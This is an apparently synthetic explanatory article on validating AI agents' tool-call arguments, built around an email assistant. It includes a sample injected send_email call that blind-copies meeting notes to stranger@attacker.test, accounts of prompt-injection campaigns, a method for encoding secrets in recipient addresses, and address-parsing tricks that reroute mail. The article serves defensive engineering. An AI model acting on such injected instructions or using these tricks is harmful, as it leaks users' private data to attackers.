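# Checking the arguments of AI agents' tool calls, and the limits of blocklists for email addresses and domains

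## Tool calls, their arguments and who can influence them

An AI agent is a language model that works on a task by calling tools in a loop and reading what they return. The tools are ordinary functions in a program, which might search a mailbox, fetch a web page or send an email. For each call, the model fills in the values the function needs, called arguments, such as a recipient or the text of a message. Programs that take input from strangers have always had to check their arguments and reject some of them. This is harder with agents because the model chooses the arguments after reading text that an attacker may have partly written. As a result, the model can supply a correctly formatted email address that belongs to the attacker.

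### From a declared tool to a running function

A developer declares each tool in advance with a name, a description and a schema, which defines the tool's named parameters in machine-readable form. The application sends these declarations to the model along with the user's message. If the model responds with a tool call, the call arrives as structured data. Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* lists three fields in a call from a Claude model: an identifier, the tool's name and an object that holds the arguments. The application reads the arguments, runs the function and returns the output to the model, which then answers the user or proposes another call. Anthropic's *How tool use works* states, "The model never runs anything on its own". OpenAI's *Function calling* describes the same cycle in five steps, and Microsoft's *Use the functions tool* also leaves execution to the developer.

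A check should therefore run after the model proposes a call and before the application executes it. The check is code that reads the proposed arguments and then allows, changes or refuses the call. After a refusal, the application can return an error to the model as the tool's result. A teaching sample in OpenAI's guide has no such check. It raises an error for a function name it does not recognise, but it passes the model's recipient and message text straight to the mail function.

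An application can't check every tool call before it runs. Anthropic runs some tools, including web search and web fetching, on its own servers, and the operation has usually finished by the time the application sees the call. A developer who wants to inspect web addresses before anything fetches them has to supply the fetching tool. Otherwise, the developer has to rely on whatever limits the provider offers.

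### An office assistant and a stranger's email

Suppose that a company with the domain example.com gives its staff an assistant. It can search mail and files, and it has the tool send_email(to, cc, bcc, subject, body, attachments). A user asks it to send the notes of Tuesday's meeting to Dana. The assistant searches the mailbox for the notes and for Dana's address, and one of the emails it reads comes from a stranger and contains an instruction to copy the notes to an outside address. If the model follows that instruction, the application receives a call like this:

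```
send_email(
  to          = ["dana@example.com"],
  cc          = [],
  bcc         = ["stranger@attacker.test"],
  subject     = "Notes from Tuesday's meeting",
  body        = "Hi Dana, here are the notes.",
  attachments = ["tuesday-notes.pdf"]
)
```

Security researchers call the stranger's method indirect prompt injection, in which an attacker plants instructions in content that the agent reads, such as an email or a web page, and the agent follows them. The harm in this case is exfiltration, which means sending private data to someone who should not have it. *Agentic AI and Security*, an article on the software engineer Martin Fowler's website, gives an example from programming. Someone asks a coding assistant for the latest issue on a project, the issue contains a planted request to post private keys on a public site, and the model may well comply. The article cites the programmer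 Simon Willison's "lethal trifecta" of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. The office assistant has all three and needs them to do its job.

The user named a person but gave no address, so the assistant had to look up the value of `to`, and who chose that value depends on where the assistant found it. If it used the company directory, the company's administrators chose the address. If it copied the address from an earlier email, whoever wrote that email chose it, and anybody can send a message under the display name Dana. The call doesn't include the source of the address.

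The user asked for no copies, so there are few innocent explanations for an address in `cc` or `bcc`. The model may have read that Dana's team leader normally gets the notes, or it may have followed the stranger's instructions. A blind copy is more dangerous than an ordinary one because Dana will not see that a third person received the message. The `to`, `cc` and `bcc` fields are destination arguments, meaning they determine where data, money or access goes. In other tools, a destination argument can be a web address, a bank account or a chat channel.

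The model writes `subject` and `body` itself, but from material that other people wrote. An attacker who cannot change the recipient may change the text instead, so that Dana gets a fraudulent link from a colleague she trusts. A link is also a kind of destination, and a check that covers only the recipient fields will miss one in the body. The model chose the file in `attachments` by matching it to the user's word "notes". Injected text could make the model choose a salary spreadsheet instead, and anyone who can write to a shared folder could put a file with a suitable name there.

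The agent also chooses whether to call send_email and how many times, but these choices don't appear in the arguments. The stranger's email could leave the message to Dana unchanged and cause a second call, addressed only to the stranger. OpenAI advises developers to assume that a response contains several calls, and a check has to examine every call.

Some of the problem can be removed by following the same guide's advice that code should fill in any value the application already has, and that the model should not be given a parameter for it. OpenAI's example is the order number in a refund. The office assistant's application already has the sender's address, so send_email has no `from` parameter. A company whose staff never use blind copies could drop `bcc` as well, though an occasional user who wanted to send one could not do so through the assistant.

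### What the attacker controls

A threat model is a statement of what an attacker can and cannot do. Wu, Nan and colleagues (2025), in *Your Mailbox Is Mine*, a study of real email agents, have a compact notation that helps here. At step *t* of a task, the agent's next action depends on a context

$$C_t = \langle P_{sys}, I_u, M_t, \Omega \rangle$$

where $P_{sys}$ is the system prompt (the developer's standing instructions), $I_u$ is the user's request, $M_t$ is the mailbox content the agent has retrieved so far, and $\Omega$ is the set of tools. The attacker knows the victim's address and can send mail to it, and so can write part of $M_t$. The attacker has no hold on the other terms, and has not broken into the user's device, the mail account, the mail server or the software that runs the agent. But the model selects its action from the whole context at once, so influence over one term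 can be influence over any argument of any call.

The same assumptions apply to agents that read web pages, shared documents or calendar invitations. The attacker writes some of what the agent reads, but does not write the user's request or the code that checks the calls. These assumptions cover an email from a colleague's hijacked account, because the attacker wrote it. They do not cover a dishonest user or a plain error, such as the model picking the wrong Dana, although a good check will catch some of those errors too.

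An agent's permissions limit how much harm its tool calls can do. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, the UK's National Cyber Security Centre tells designers to assume the impact will be the worst that could happen if an attacker had direct access to the tools.

### Why the check must lie outside the model

The easiest defence to add is a line in the system prompt that tells the model to ignore instructions in emails. This helps somewhat but is not enough. ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks* quotes the agency's explanation that a language model does not separate data from instructions internally and only predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from the text. The NCSC's title compares prompt injection with SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form ends up running as a database command. Programmers can prevent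 SQL injection by sending the command and the data to the database separately. Nobody has an equivalent for language models, and the agency thinks it very possible that no one will ever stop prompt injection as completely. It describes the model as an "inherently confusable deputy", meaning that the model has authority which an outsider can trick it into using.

Wu and colleagues measured the model's own resistance by the attack success rate, the share of attempted attacks whose harmful effect the agent carries out. Standard injection templates, which openly compete with the system prompt and the user's request, succeeded in only 4.58% to 8.13% of trials. Emails the researchers designed for mail agents succeeded in 353 of 480 controlled trials (73.54%), and the method eventually hijacked all 63 applications they tested. System prompts and safety training therefore stop crude attempts, but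 an attacker can choose the email and keep rewriting it.

For this reason the NCSC wants designers to focus on deterministic safeguards, which do not use a language model, to limit what the system can do. Code that checks a recipient against a list gives the same result however persuasive the stranger's email was, because the code never reads the email. A second language model that reads the conversation and judges the call may be a useful extra layer, but it also reads the attacker's text.

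The information the check relies on must also be outside the model's control, which is easier to get wrong. If send_email had a `user_approved` argument and the check relied on it, the stranger would only need to get the model to set it to true. A list of permitted recipients has the same flaw if the agent can edit the file that contains it.

### Injection in real email

Until recently, most injected text targeted AI security tools. Scholten and Filar (2026) wrote in June, in *Adversarial prompt injection payload for evading AI-based detection*, that almost all the injection seen by their company, the email security firm Sublime Security, was meant to trick these tools into classing harmful emails as harmless. On 7 October, Mascellino (2026) reported in *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* that the security firm Barracuda had found phishing emails designed to manipulate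 both AI assistants and their users.

Then, on 22 October, Sublime observed an invoice fraud that included instructions for agents that can act on mail. Sublime Security's *Shut down prompt injection attacks targeting AI email agents and tools* lists the company's 26 October report on the campaign, and Trent's (2026) *Prompt Injection Goes After the Inbox* recounts the details. The emails carried invoices for about $88,000 that falsely appeared to come from a North American cybersecurity company. They posed as messages from a co-founder or chief executive of the target organisation, included a fabricated reply chain, and offered a 10% discount that would soon expire. They usually went to a financial controller. The emails also contained text that mail programs do not display, which instructed an agent to forward the email and its PDF, unchanged, to an accounts-payable address at the target's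 own domain.

No data was to leave the company, so this was not exfiltration. The attackers apparently hoped that the invoice would enter the payment queue as routine internal mail. Sublime tried the message on several models: some never surfaced the hidden text, some included it in a summary, and some recognised the injection and recommended reporting it. Trent mentions no agent that actually forwarded an invoice. The campaign is good evidence of what attackers are now attempting, and says little about how often they succeed. (Sublime calls an attack of this sort "direct" injection and keeps "indirect" for attempts to mislead security scanners. In the more common usage both are indirect, because in both the attacker plants the instruction in content.)

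### Four questions about a value

It helps to divide what developers often call "validating" a tool call into four separate checks, because a value can pass one and fail the next.

One check is whether the value is well formed. An email address should look like an email address, and a list of recipients should be a list. The bare word "Dana" in the `to` field fails this check, but the stranger's address passes. This is the most familiar kind of validation, which means deciding whether a value is acceptable and refusing the call if it is not.

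An argument can be unsafe for the program that receives it, because mail servers, databases and browsers treat certain characters as commands or separators. In badly written mail software, for instance, a line break in the subject can start a new header and so add a recipient. The usual remedy is sanitisation, which makes a value safe to pass on by removing parts of it or escaping them (marking them as plain text). Unlike validation, sanitisation lets the call go ahead with a slightly different value from the one the model proposed. It does not stop an email from going to a stranger's address, which contains no dangerous characters.

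To check whether a value is permitted, a developer can use a blocklist, which names forbidden values and allows everything else, or an allowlist, which names permitted values and refuses everything else. A blocklist lets through an address that nobody has reported yet, which is a serious weakness because an attacker can register a new domain in minutes. An allowlist stops such an address, and one that held only example.com would have kept the meeting notes from the stranger. But it also stops the user from writing to a new client. Refusing a legitimate call in this way is called a false refusal, and users of a system that produces many of them will soon ask for a way around it.

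A check could test whether the user's task called for the recipient. The user asked for the notes to go to Dana, so the check could refuse any other recipient, inside or outside the company. The rule has to come from the user's request, not from anything the agent read afterwards, and requests are often vague about the values that matter. The October invoice emails show why the effort may be worthwhile. Their accounts-payable address was well formed, contained nothing that would cause problems for a mail server, and was on the company's own domain, which almost any allowlist would include. It was wrong only because no user had asked for the invoice to go there.

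## Checking the type, format and length of arguments

A developer can start checking that a tool call's arguments are well formed by comparing them with the schema already sent to the model to describe the tool. Most tool-calling interfaces use JSON Schema, a standard language for describing what a piece of JSON (a text format for structured data) may contain. Whether this check runs depends on the interface, the software library and some settings that are off by default.

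### A schema for send_email

The schema below covers the office assistant's mail tool. It adds one parameter, `importance`, which mail programs display as a flag.

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "to":  { "type": "array", "minItems": 1, "maxItems": 5,
             "items": { "$ref": "#/$defs/address" } },
    "cc":  { "type": "array", "maxItems": 5,
             "items": { "$ref": "#/$defs/address" } },
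    "bcc": { "type": "array", "maxItems": 1,
             "items": { "$ref": "#/$defs/address" } },
    "subject": { "type": "string", "maxLength": 150,
                 "pattern": "^[^\\r\\n]*$" },
    "body": { "type": "string", "maxLength": 5000 },
    "importance": { "type": "string", "enum": ["normal", "high"] },
    "attachments": { "type": "array", "maxItems": 3,
      "items": { "type": "string", "maxLength": 100,
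                 "pattern": "^[A-Za-z0-9_-]+\\.(pdf|docx)$" } }
  },
  "required": ["to", "cc", "bcc", "subject", "body",
               "importance", "attachments"],
  "additionalProperties": false,
  "$defs": {
    "address": { "type": "string", "format": "email", "maxLength": 254,
      "pattern": "^[A-Za-z0-9._+-]{1,64}@[A-Za-z0-9-]+(\\.[A-Za-z0-9-]+)+$" }
  }
}
```

The `type` rules reject values of the wrong type. Because `to` must be a list, a call that passes two addresses in one comma-separated string fails. Without the rule, a mail library that splits strings at commas would send the message to both addresses, while a check designed for a single address might look only at the first. The `required` list rejects calls that omit a field, which would otherwise crash halfway through the function or use a forgotten default.

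JSON Schema permits fields that the schema does not mention unless the developer sets `additionalProperties` to false. If the model added a `reply_to` field and the application passed all the arguments to a mail library, Dana's reply could go to a stranger even though every recipient of the original message was correct. The `enum` on `importance` allows only two values, so no free text reaches the mail header that holds the value.

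The `pattern` rules are regular expressions, which describe sets of strings. The signs `^` and `$` anchor a pattern to the start and end of the value. JSON Schema doesn't anchor patterns itself, so without these signs a whole paragraph containing an address would pass as an address. Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025) found a similar mistake in how one of the eight coding agents whose security they studied in *Takedown* checked its list of permitted commands. The agent looked for a permitted command anywhere in the line, so it would run a destructive command that merely mentioned a permitted one in a comment. Python's `$` also matches just before a line break at the end of a string, so a program that runs these patterns in Python should refuse a final line break separately.

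The address pattern is narrower than the mail standards, so it will reject some valid addresses, such as o'brien@example.com (an apostrophe is legal before the @) and addresses in non-Latin scripts. It also accepts a few strings that mail servers reject, such as an address with two dots in a row. A proper address parser checks addresses better than any pattern of reasonable length. The attachment pattern is deliberately narrow. It excludes slashes so that the argument can't contain a path to a file in another folder.

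`maxItems` caps the number of recipients per call. A total of eleven is plenty for meeting notes, and the cap prevents a single call from emailing the entire staff. It doesn't prevent a hundred calls to eleven people each, so the application also needs to limit the number of calls per task.

### Who enforces the schema

A model reads a tool's schema along with the rest of the prompt and usually complies, but sending the schema does not enforce it. According to Anthropic's *Strict tool use*, Claude may return the text "2" where the schema requires the number 2, or omit a required field. Both Anthropic and OpenAI offer a strict mode that developers switch on for each tool. In Anthropic's version, software compiles the schema into a grammar and, as the model writes the call token by token, excludes any token that would break the grammar. Strict mode covers only part of JSON Schema, and the two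 companies leave out different parts. The table draws on Anthropic's *Structured outputs* and OpenAI's *Structured outputs*.

| Constraint | Anthropic, strict mode | OpenAI, strict mode |
|---|---|---|
| `type` | guaranteed | guaranteed |
| `required` | guaranteed; optional fields allowed | every field must be required |
| `additionalProperties: false` | compulsory | compulsory |
| `enum` | guaranteed except for capitalisation | guaranteed |
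| `pattern` | simple patterns only | supported |
| `format: email` | supported | supported |
| `maxLength` | refused with an error | not on the supported list |
| `maxItems` | refused with an error | supported |

So neither provider will enforce the whole send_email schema. A developer who wants strict mode has to send a reduced version and check the arguments against the full one inside the application. OpenAI's fine-tuned models also don't support patterns, formats or limits on list length.

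Despite these guarantees, the output may not match the schema if Claude refuses a request or the reply is cut off at its length limit. OpenAI describes the same two exceptions. An application should therefore check why the model stopped before using the arguments. Claude may also return a value from a fixed list with different capitalisation and no error, so Anthropic advises ignoring case when comparing these values. A request can include at most 20 strict tools, so an agent with more should reserve strict mode for tools that change something or send something out.

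Requiring every field can also lead the model to invent values. If the assistant never found Dana's address, for example, it may make one up to fill a required `to` field. OpenAI warns that a model may invent values to fit the schema even when the input is unrelated to it. The usual solution is to let the field be null and have the application ask the user for the value when it is.

The effect of the `format` keyword depends on the software that processes it. In the strict modes, `"format": "email"` restricts what the model can write. In an ordinary JSON Schema validator, it is by default only an annotation, so it doesn't cause any value to be rejected. JSON Schema (2022) defines `type` and the other structural keywords as assertions, which a value must satisfy, and covers `format` separately. Until 2019, format checking was on by default, although a validator might not have implemented it.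 JSON Schema's *Release notes* (2019) describe the newer behaviour as "predictably off by default". According to dev.harrel:json-schema's *Format validation*, the keyword "performs no validation" in that Java library until the developer installs an extra package and attaches it. If a developer relies on the keyword alone, the word "Dana" could pass as an email address. For this reason, the schema above has a pattern as well as the format. The easiest safeguard is a test that confirms the validator rejects a bad address.

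Many tools now come from outside the application. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for connecting agents to servers that offer tools, and its current specification dates from 28 July 2026. The specification calls the application that holds the model the client. The Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) states that servers MUST validate all tool inputs and limit how often clients can call a tool. Its rules for clients are mostly recommendations. A client SHOULD show the user the inputs before it calls the server, to avoid exfiltration, and SHOULD ask for confirmation of sensitive operations.

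The server's developer is therefore responsible for the required check. The developer knows what a valid date looks like, but does not know that this user only wanted to write to Dana.

A Model Context Protocol (MCP) server reports an unknown tool as a protocol error, and a bad argument as a tool result marked as an error. The title of *SEP-1303*, "Input Validation Errors as Tool Execution Errors", suggests that this difference is deliberate. Clients should pass these tool results to the model so that it can correct the argument and try again. Retrying is useful when the model has mistyped a date, but when a recipient has been refused, it gives a model that is following injected instructions another chance. The check therefore has to run on every attempt, and the application should stop after a few.

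In MCP's default version of JSON Schema, `format` is only an annotation. The Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) also treats the schema as possibly written by an attacker, which makes sense when a third party runs the server. It says software must not automatically fetch parts of a schema from the network, and should limit a schema's depth or the time spent validating it, since a malicious schema could tie up the validator.

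Software may not meet the requirements in its specification. Hungerford (2026), in *Measuring tool input schema fidelity*, reports that neither the TypeScript nor the Python development kit for MCP faithfully checks inputs against the current version of JSON Schema out of the box, so a server's author has to add a suitable validator. Hungerford also tested 24 models on the schemas of six demonstration tools, mostly with 20 trials per pairing and with strict mode off where it applied. Most models filled in most schemas correctly every time, but results varied with the company hosting the model. For example, gpt-oss-120b failed every trial of the tool with fixed choices at three hosts and passed every trial at two others.

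Those prompts were cooperative, but Hungerford also ran a control that told a model to break the schema, and the host, Deepinfra, let the invalid output through. Injected text can make the same demand, so valid output on ordinary requests is poor evidence that a model's output will follow the schema under attack. The US National Security Agency's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) likewise holds that secure defaults depend on careful implementation and validation tools, along with clearer specifications. The application should run its own validator on every call, with the full schema and format checking switched on, whatever the provider or server guarantees.

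### The name of the tool

An interface can also leave the tool name in a call unchecked. Applications usually assume that this name is one of those they supplied. Lee and colleagues found in 2025 that Anthropic's interface did not check this, while the interfaces for OpenAI's, Google's and xAI's models did. No standard specified whether the interface or the application was responsible for the check, and an agent that relied on the interface could skip it altogether.

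Two of the eight coding agents in the study could be made to run tools that were supposed to be disabled, such as a file-writing tool in read-only mode. In one of the two, a value in the model's own tool call also determined whether a command needed the user's approval, which is the same weakness as in the `user_approved` argument imagined earlier. A schema would not have helped there, since true and false are both valid values for a true-or-false field.

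Anthropic has since changed its interface for developers who opt in. Its *Structured outputs on the Claude Developer Platform* (2025) announced schema guarantees for tool calls as a public beta on 14 November 2025, and they became generally available on 4 February 2026. With strict mode on, the name is now "always valid", according to Anthropic. Nobody seems to have repeated the test and published the results for tools without strict mode, so it is safer to assume that the 2025 result still holds for them.

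Lee and colleagues recommend that the agent check the tool's name in any case, which takes about one line of code. The application looks the name up in a table of only the tools enabled for this user and this task, because a table of every function in the program would also include disabled tools.

### What length limits are for

RFC 5321, the standard for passing mail between servers, limits the part of an email address before the @ to 64 octets (units of eight bits). It limits the whole address to 256 octets including the angle brackets around it, which leaves 254 for the address itself. JSON Schema counts characters instead, and a character outside the English alphabet can take up to four octets. The address pattern above allows only one-octet characters, so the two counts agree.

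One reason to check an argument's length is to save resources. A model stuck in a loop can write an enormous argument, and some regular expressions become extremely slow on long strings. Programs should therefore check the length before they run any regular expression.

A shorter field also has less room for planted text. Another agent may well read the email that this one sends, and a long subject could carry instructions to it. Length limits also help with fields that outsiders fill in. In ForcedLeak, an attack that researchers demonstrated on Salesforce's agents in 2025, the planted instructions were in a web form field that accepted 42,000 characters.

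Length also bounds how much a single call can leak, and here even an address is roomier than it looks. The owner of a domain can set up its mail server to accept every address at that domain, whatever comes before the @. An attacker who owns attacker.test can therefore have the agent write a secret into the address itself. If each of the 64 characters is one of 36 letters and digits, the part before the @ carries

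$$64 \times \log_2 36 \approx 64 \times 5.17 \approx 331 \text{ bits} \approx 41 \text{ bytes}$$

A 256-bit encryption key takes up only 50 of those characters. The message can deliver the key even with an empty body and no attachment.

The domain part of an address can also carry data, because the owner of attacker.test can receive mail at any of its subdomains. An address of the full 254 characters has room for 237 letters and digits of the attacker's choice, or about 153 bytes, after allowing for the dots and the domain's own name. The send_email schema permits eleven such addresses per call. A 5,000-character body can carry far more, but the address matters when a filter scans the body and attachments for secrets and doesn't scan the recipient.

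Tighter limits reduce the leak but don't stop it. Few people's addresses have 64 characters before the @, and a cap of 30 would reduce the 41 bytes to 19. But that cap would also reject some of the long reply addresses that mailing lists and help desks generate, and an attacker could still split the secret over several calls. It is best to base such limits on the longest values in a few months of ordinary mail and add some margin.

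### The stranger's address passes

The call that the stranger's email produced, with `importance` set to "normal", goes through the full schema like this:

```
to            1 address (1 to 5 allowed)                pass
cc            0 addresses (up to 5 allowed)             pass
bcc           1 address (up to 1 allowed)               pass
  stranger@attacker.test
              text, 22 characters (limit 254)           pass
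              8 characters before the @ (limit 64)      pass
              address pattern and email format          pass
subject       28 characters (limit 150), one line       pass
body          28 characters (limit 5,000)               pass
importance    "normal"                                  pass
attachments   1 file, acceptable name and type          pass
extra fields  none                                      pass
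```

Stricter limits on the number of recipients would not prevent this. If `bcc` is capped at zero, the agent can still put the attacker's address in `cc`, or in the `to` field of a second call. Strict mode does not help either, since it only guarantees that the call matches the schema, and a call that sends email to the attacker can do so.

The Model Context Protocol makes a similar distinction for handles, the identifiers that a server gives out for things like a shopping basket. Its guidance treats a handle as a name, not proof of permission, so the server should check on every call whether the caller may use it. An email address is also a name that doesn't prove permission. A developer could reject the stranger's address by ending the pattern in `@example\.com$`, but that rule is an allowlist written as a regular expression, so somebody has to decide which domains belong in it.

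## Normalising addresses and making values safe to pass on

To enforce a rule that permits only example.com, a program has to decide whether a given string is an address at example.com. It should parse the string (split it into its parts) and then normalise it (rewrite it in one standard form, so that two spellings of the same thing compare as equal). Just searching the string for the permitted name works for most ordinary addresses, but an attacker who can influence a tool call's arguments can supply an unusual one for which the search gives the wrong answer.

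### Six recipients and three checks

Suppose the office assistant may email only addresses at example.com, and its mail tool accepts each recipient as free text. The table compares three checks. Two are case-sensitive text searches. The third parses the string, rejects it unless it contains exactly one address, converts the domain to lower case and compares the whole domain with example.com.

| Recipient string | Where the mail goes | Contains "example.com" | Ends with "example.com" | Parsed domain is exactly example.com |
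|---|---|---|---|---|
| `dana@example.com` | Dana | admits | admits | admits |
| `dana@EXAMPLE.COM` | Dana | refuses | refuses | admits |
| `dana@lists.example.com` | a subdomain | admits | admits | refuses |
| `dana@example.com.attacker.test` | the attacker | admits | refuses | refuses |
| `"dana@example.com" <stranger@attacker.test>` | the attacker | admits | refuses | refuses |
| `stranger@attacker.test, dana@example.com` | the attacker and Dana | admits | admits | refuses |

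The "contains" check admits all three strings that send mail to the attacker. The "ends with" check admits only the one with two addresses, but it would also admit an address at notexample.com, a separate domain that anyone can register. Both checks reject Dana's own address when its domain is in capitals.

Whether to permit subdomains is a policy decision. The owner of example.com controls lists.example.com, but may have let an outside newsletter firm run it. A developer who wants to permit every subdomain should test for the ending `.example.com`, including the leading dot.

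Checking only the start of a domain fails too. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-24052 Detail*, Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code checked for trusted web domains this way before version 1.0.111. An attacker could register a longer domain that began with a trusted name, and the agent could then send requests there without the user's consent.

### What an email address can contain

In mail standards, the local part of an address is the part before the @. A recipient string can also include a display name, which mail programs show to people but mail servers ignore. In `"dana@example.com" <stranger@attacker.test>`, Dana's address is only the display name, and the mail goes to the address in angle brackets.

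A local part in quotation marks may contain another @, so a program that splits the string at the first @ can get the wrong domain. Poh (2025) found in *Gotchas in Email Parsing* that the default pattern in Hibernate Validator, a Java library, accepts such addresses. Splitting at the last @ is also unsafe, because Jakarta Mail, another Java library, delivers to an address in angle brackets even if more text follows it. If that text ends in @example.com, a check for example.com after the last @ will approve a message that goes somewhere else.

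One string can hold several addresses, separated by commas or written in an old group notation. In *Applicability Statement for IETF Core Email Protocols*, a draft internet standard, Klensin and Murchison (2026) note that the group notation has had little use and that some software may not support it. Poh found that Jakarta Mail still accepts it. A tool whose `to` field is already a list needs neither form, so the check should refuse any item that contains more than one address.

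It is harder to tell when two local parts mean the same mailbox. Many mail systems deliver dana+notes@example.com to Dana and treat the text after the plus sign as a label, and some also ignore dots. Others treat each spelling as a separate mailbox. The standard allows even "Smith" and "smith" to be different users, although most systems treat them as one. Klensin and Murchison conclude that only the system that finally delivers the mail can interpret a local part properly, and that other software should leave it unchanged.

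A check can put the domain in lower case, because domain names are not case-sensitive, but it should leave the local part unchanged. A company knows how its own mail system treats tags and dots, so it can apply those rules when comparing addresses at its own domain, but it would be guessing at the rules for other domains. Removing a tag from an outside address could make an unapproved mailbox match an approved one, so it is safer to treat the tagged address as new.

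Programmers have known for decades that a line break in a value can add a mail header, but mail libraries still sometimes fail to block one. Red Hat's *CVE-2026-1299* describes a flaw in Python's standard email module that could let an attacker change a message's recipients, body or apparent sender. The flaw affected only programs that used one class to write headers. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Nodemailer package* lists two similar flaws from 2026 in Nodemailer, a mail library for JavaScript. One allowed line breaks in the comments of mailing-list headers, and the other allowed them in a connection setting, where they could add commands to those sent to the mail server. A check should refuse line breaks in every argument that ends up in a header, including display names and the file names of attachments.

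### When the check and the mail software disagree

Even an exact comparison fails if the check and the mail software extract different domains from the same string. In 2024, Gareth Heyes of the web security company PortSwigger showed in *Splitting the email atom* that this was possible in several well-known products. The paper starts with routing notations from the early days of email. The mail servers Sendmail 8.15.2 and Postfix 3.6.4 still recognised some of them, and delivered mail for certain addresses ending in @example.com to another domain.

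Heyes then tested encoded words, a notation for writing non-English letters in mail headers. A Ruby mail library with over 500 million downloads also decoded them inside addresses. An address could pass a website's checks in its encoded form, and the library would then decode it into characters that cut the address short. With this method, Heyes got GitHub to mark addresses at microsoft.com, mozilla.com and github.com as verified on a test account. A company that used GitHub-verified addresses to control access to an internal site could have let a stranger in. GitLab and Zendesk, a provider of customer-support software, had related faults. GitLab fixed its fault in April 2024, and GitHub and Zendesk fixed theirs in May.

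Heyes concluded that it is never safe to control access by email domain. Checking addresses is easier for an agent that sends mail, because it only needs to know where a message will go and can refuse unusual addresses with little downside.

Researchers have since found similar faults in Nodemailer. According to GitLab's *CVE-2025-13033* (2025), the library misread quoted local parts that contained an @, and sent mail to the address inside the quotation marks. The finder, who publishes as xclow3n, had used the bug in a university hacking contest in 2024, but the advisory and the fix came only in October 2025. OSV's *GHSA-5jpx-9hw9-2fx4* (2025) describes how an attacker could exploit the bug in NextAuth.js, a sign-in library that used Nodemailer, to receive sign-in emails meant for someone else.

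Two more faults in version 9.0.6 became public in 2026. Docker Scout's *GHSA-wmmp-3585-3rmp* deals with the soft hyphen, an invisible character that marks where a word may be split. Browsers and other software that follows the Unicode rules for domain names drop this character. A check that used such software therefore found the trusted domain, but Nodemailer kept the character and produced a different domain.

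The other fault involved comments, remarks in parentheses that mail standards permit in addresses. Docker Scout's *GHSA-cc9r-2j5m-2m83* explains that when a comment stood between two domain names, Nodemailer removed it and joined the names into a third domain, which an attacker could register. Given such a string, Python's strict parser stops at the comment and returns the trusted domain, with a warning that the calling program may never check. But Python's `getaddresses` function joins the names, as Nodemailer did.

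Both advisories rate the faults as moderate, and version 9.1.0 fixed them. The soft hyphen is less of a threat in .com addresses, because the .com rules do not allow it in registered names. The repair first suggested for the soft hyphen had a worse flaw, because the replacement function stops reading a domain at a slash and so could have turned an undeliverable address into a working one at an attacker's domain.

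### Parse, refuse, normalise, compare, pass on

Developers cannot count on finding a mail library without such bugs, so it is more practical to give the library only unambiguous addresses. The function below parses the recipient once, rejects anything ambiguous, normalises the domain, compares it with the list, and returns the parsed address for the mail library to use.

```python
import re
from email.utils import getaddresses

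PLAIN = re.compile(
    r"[A-Za-z0-9._+-]{1,64}@[A-Za-z0-9-]+(\.[A-Za-z0-9-]+)+")

def approved_recipient(raw, permitted_domains):
    if len(raw) > 254:
        raise ValueError("too long")
    parsed = getaddresses([raw])                  # parse once
    if len(parsed) != 1 or parsed[0][1] != raw:   # refuse ambiguity
        raise ValueError("not a single plain address")
    address = parsed[0][1]
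    if not PLAIN.fullmatch(address):
        raise ValueError("unusual characters")
    local, domain = address.rsplit("@", 1)
    domain = domain.lower()                       # normalise
    if domain not in permitted_domains:           # compare
        raise ValueError("domain not permitted")
    return f"{local}@{domain}"                    # pass on the parsed value
```

The length check comes first because GitLab's list also includes address strings that take Nodemailer so long to parse that the program freezes. Current versions of Python's `getaddresses` reject malformed input by default. However, OSV's *CVE-2023-27043* records that the email module, up to Python 3.11.3, could take the wrong part of a header as the address, which could let an outsider past a sign-up rule meant for one company's staff.

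The test `parsed[0][1] != raw` rejects any string that the parser changed, for example by removing a display name or a comment. `PLAIN` is the address pattern from the send_email schema, and `fullmatch` requires it to match the whole string, including any final line break. All the parser disagreements described so far depended on a character that this pattern excludes, such as a quotation mark, a parenthesis, an angle bracket or a soft hyphen.

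The original string should go no further than this function. In the soft-hyphen case, the check correctly worked out the trusted domain, but the application gave Nodemailer the original string. If it had passed on the parsed address, the mail would have gone to the domain the check had approved.

Because it uses the schema's pattern, the function also refuses o'brien@example.com and other valid but unusual addresses. Klensin and Murchison advise mail systems that relay messages to accept strange-looking addresses unless they break the standard. This makes sense for a server that carries other people's mail, but an agent's application can be stricter because it can ask the user about a refused address. A company with many names like O'Brien can add the apostrophe to the pattern.

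`permitted_domains` must be a set or a list. If a developer passes the string "example.com" instead, Python's `in` checks for a substring, so the function would accept an address at ample.com.

### Domains and web addresses

In the Domain Name System (DNS), which translates domain names into network addresses, "example.com." with a final dot is the same domain as "example.com". The mail standard forbids the dot, but some systems accept it, and Klensin and Murchison encourage stripping it. The function above rejects it. A program that accepts the dot has to remove it before comparing domains, or the two spellings won't match.

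DNS names use a small set of characters, so software converts other letters into a code called Punycode. PortSwigger's example is münchen.com, which becomes xn--mnchen-3ya.com. A program that accepts such domains should convert them before comparing them, and give the mail library the converted form. Otherwise, the library will do its own conversion and may get a different result, as Nodemailer did.

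Lookalike letters mainly mislead people. The Cyrillic letter а looks the same as the Latin a on most screens, but the two have different character codes, so an exact comparison will tell them apart. A user asked to confirm a recipient may miss the difference, and so may an administrator who adds domains to the list. Showing them the Punycode form of any domain with non-Latin letters helps, but it won't expose a lookalike made of ordinary characters, such as the digit 1 in place of the letter l.

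A tool that fetches web pages needs a parser for web addresses. The syntax allows a username before the domain, so `https://example.com@attacker.test/` leads to attacker.test, although a check on the start of the string would find example.com. Few fetching tools need a username there, so the tool's address check can refuse any address that has one.

Checking the address once is also not enough, because the server can respond with a redirect to another address. Many web libraries follow redirects automatically. The tool should turn this off and check each new address before requesting it.

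### Escaping, stripping and refusing

Refusing unusual characters works for recipients, but a message body or search term may need to contain almost any character. The program should escape special characters in these values so that they are treated as plain text. For example, if send_email sends messages as HTML, a `<` in the body should become `&lt;`. This also prevents the model from writing a link whose visible text hides its real destination.

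The same escape would not protect a database query. MDN's *Input validation*, a guide for web developers, explains that general checks cannot be the main defence against such attacks, because it is extremely hard to protect a value without knowing where a program will use it. The code that builds the HTML or the query should therefore escape the value as its last step.

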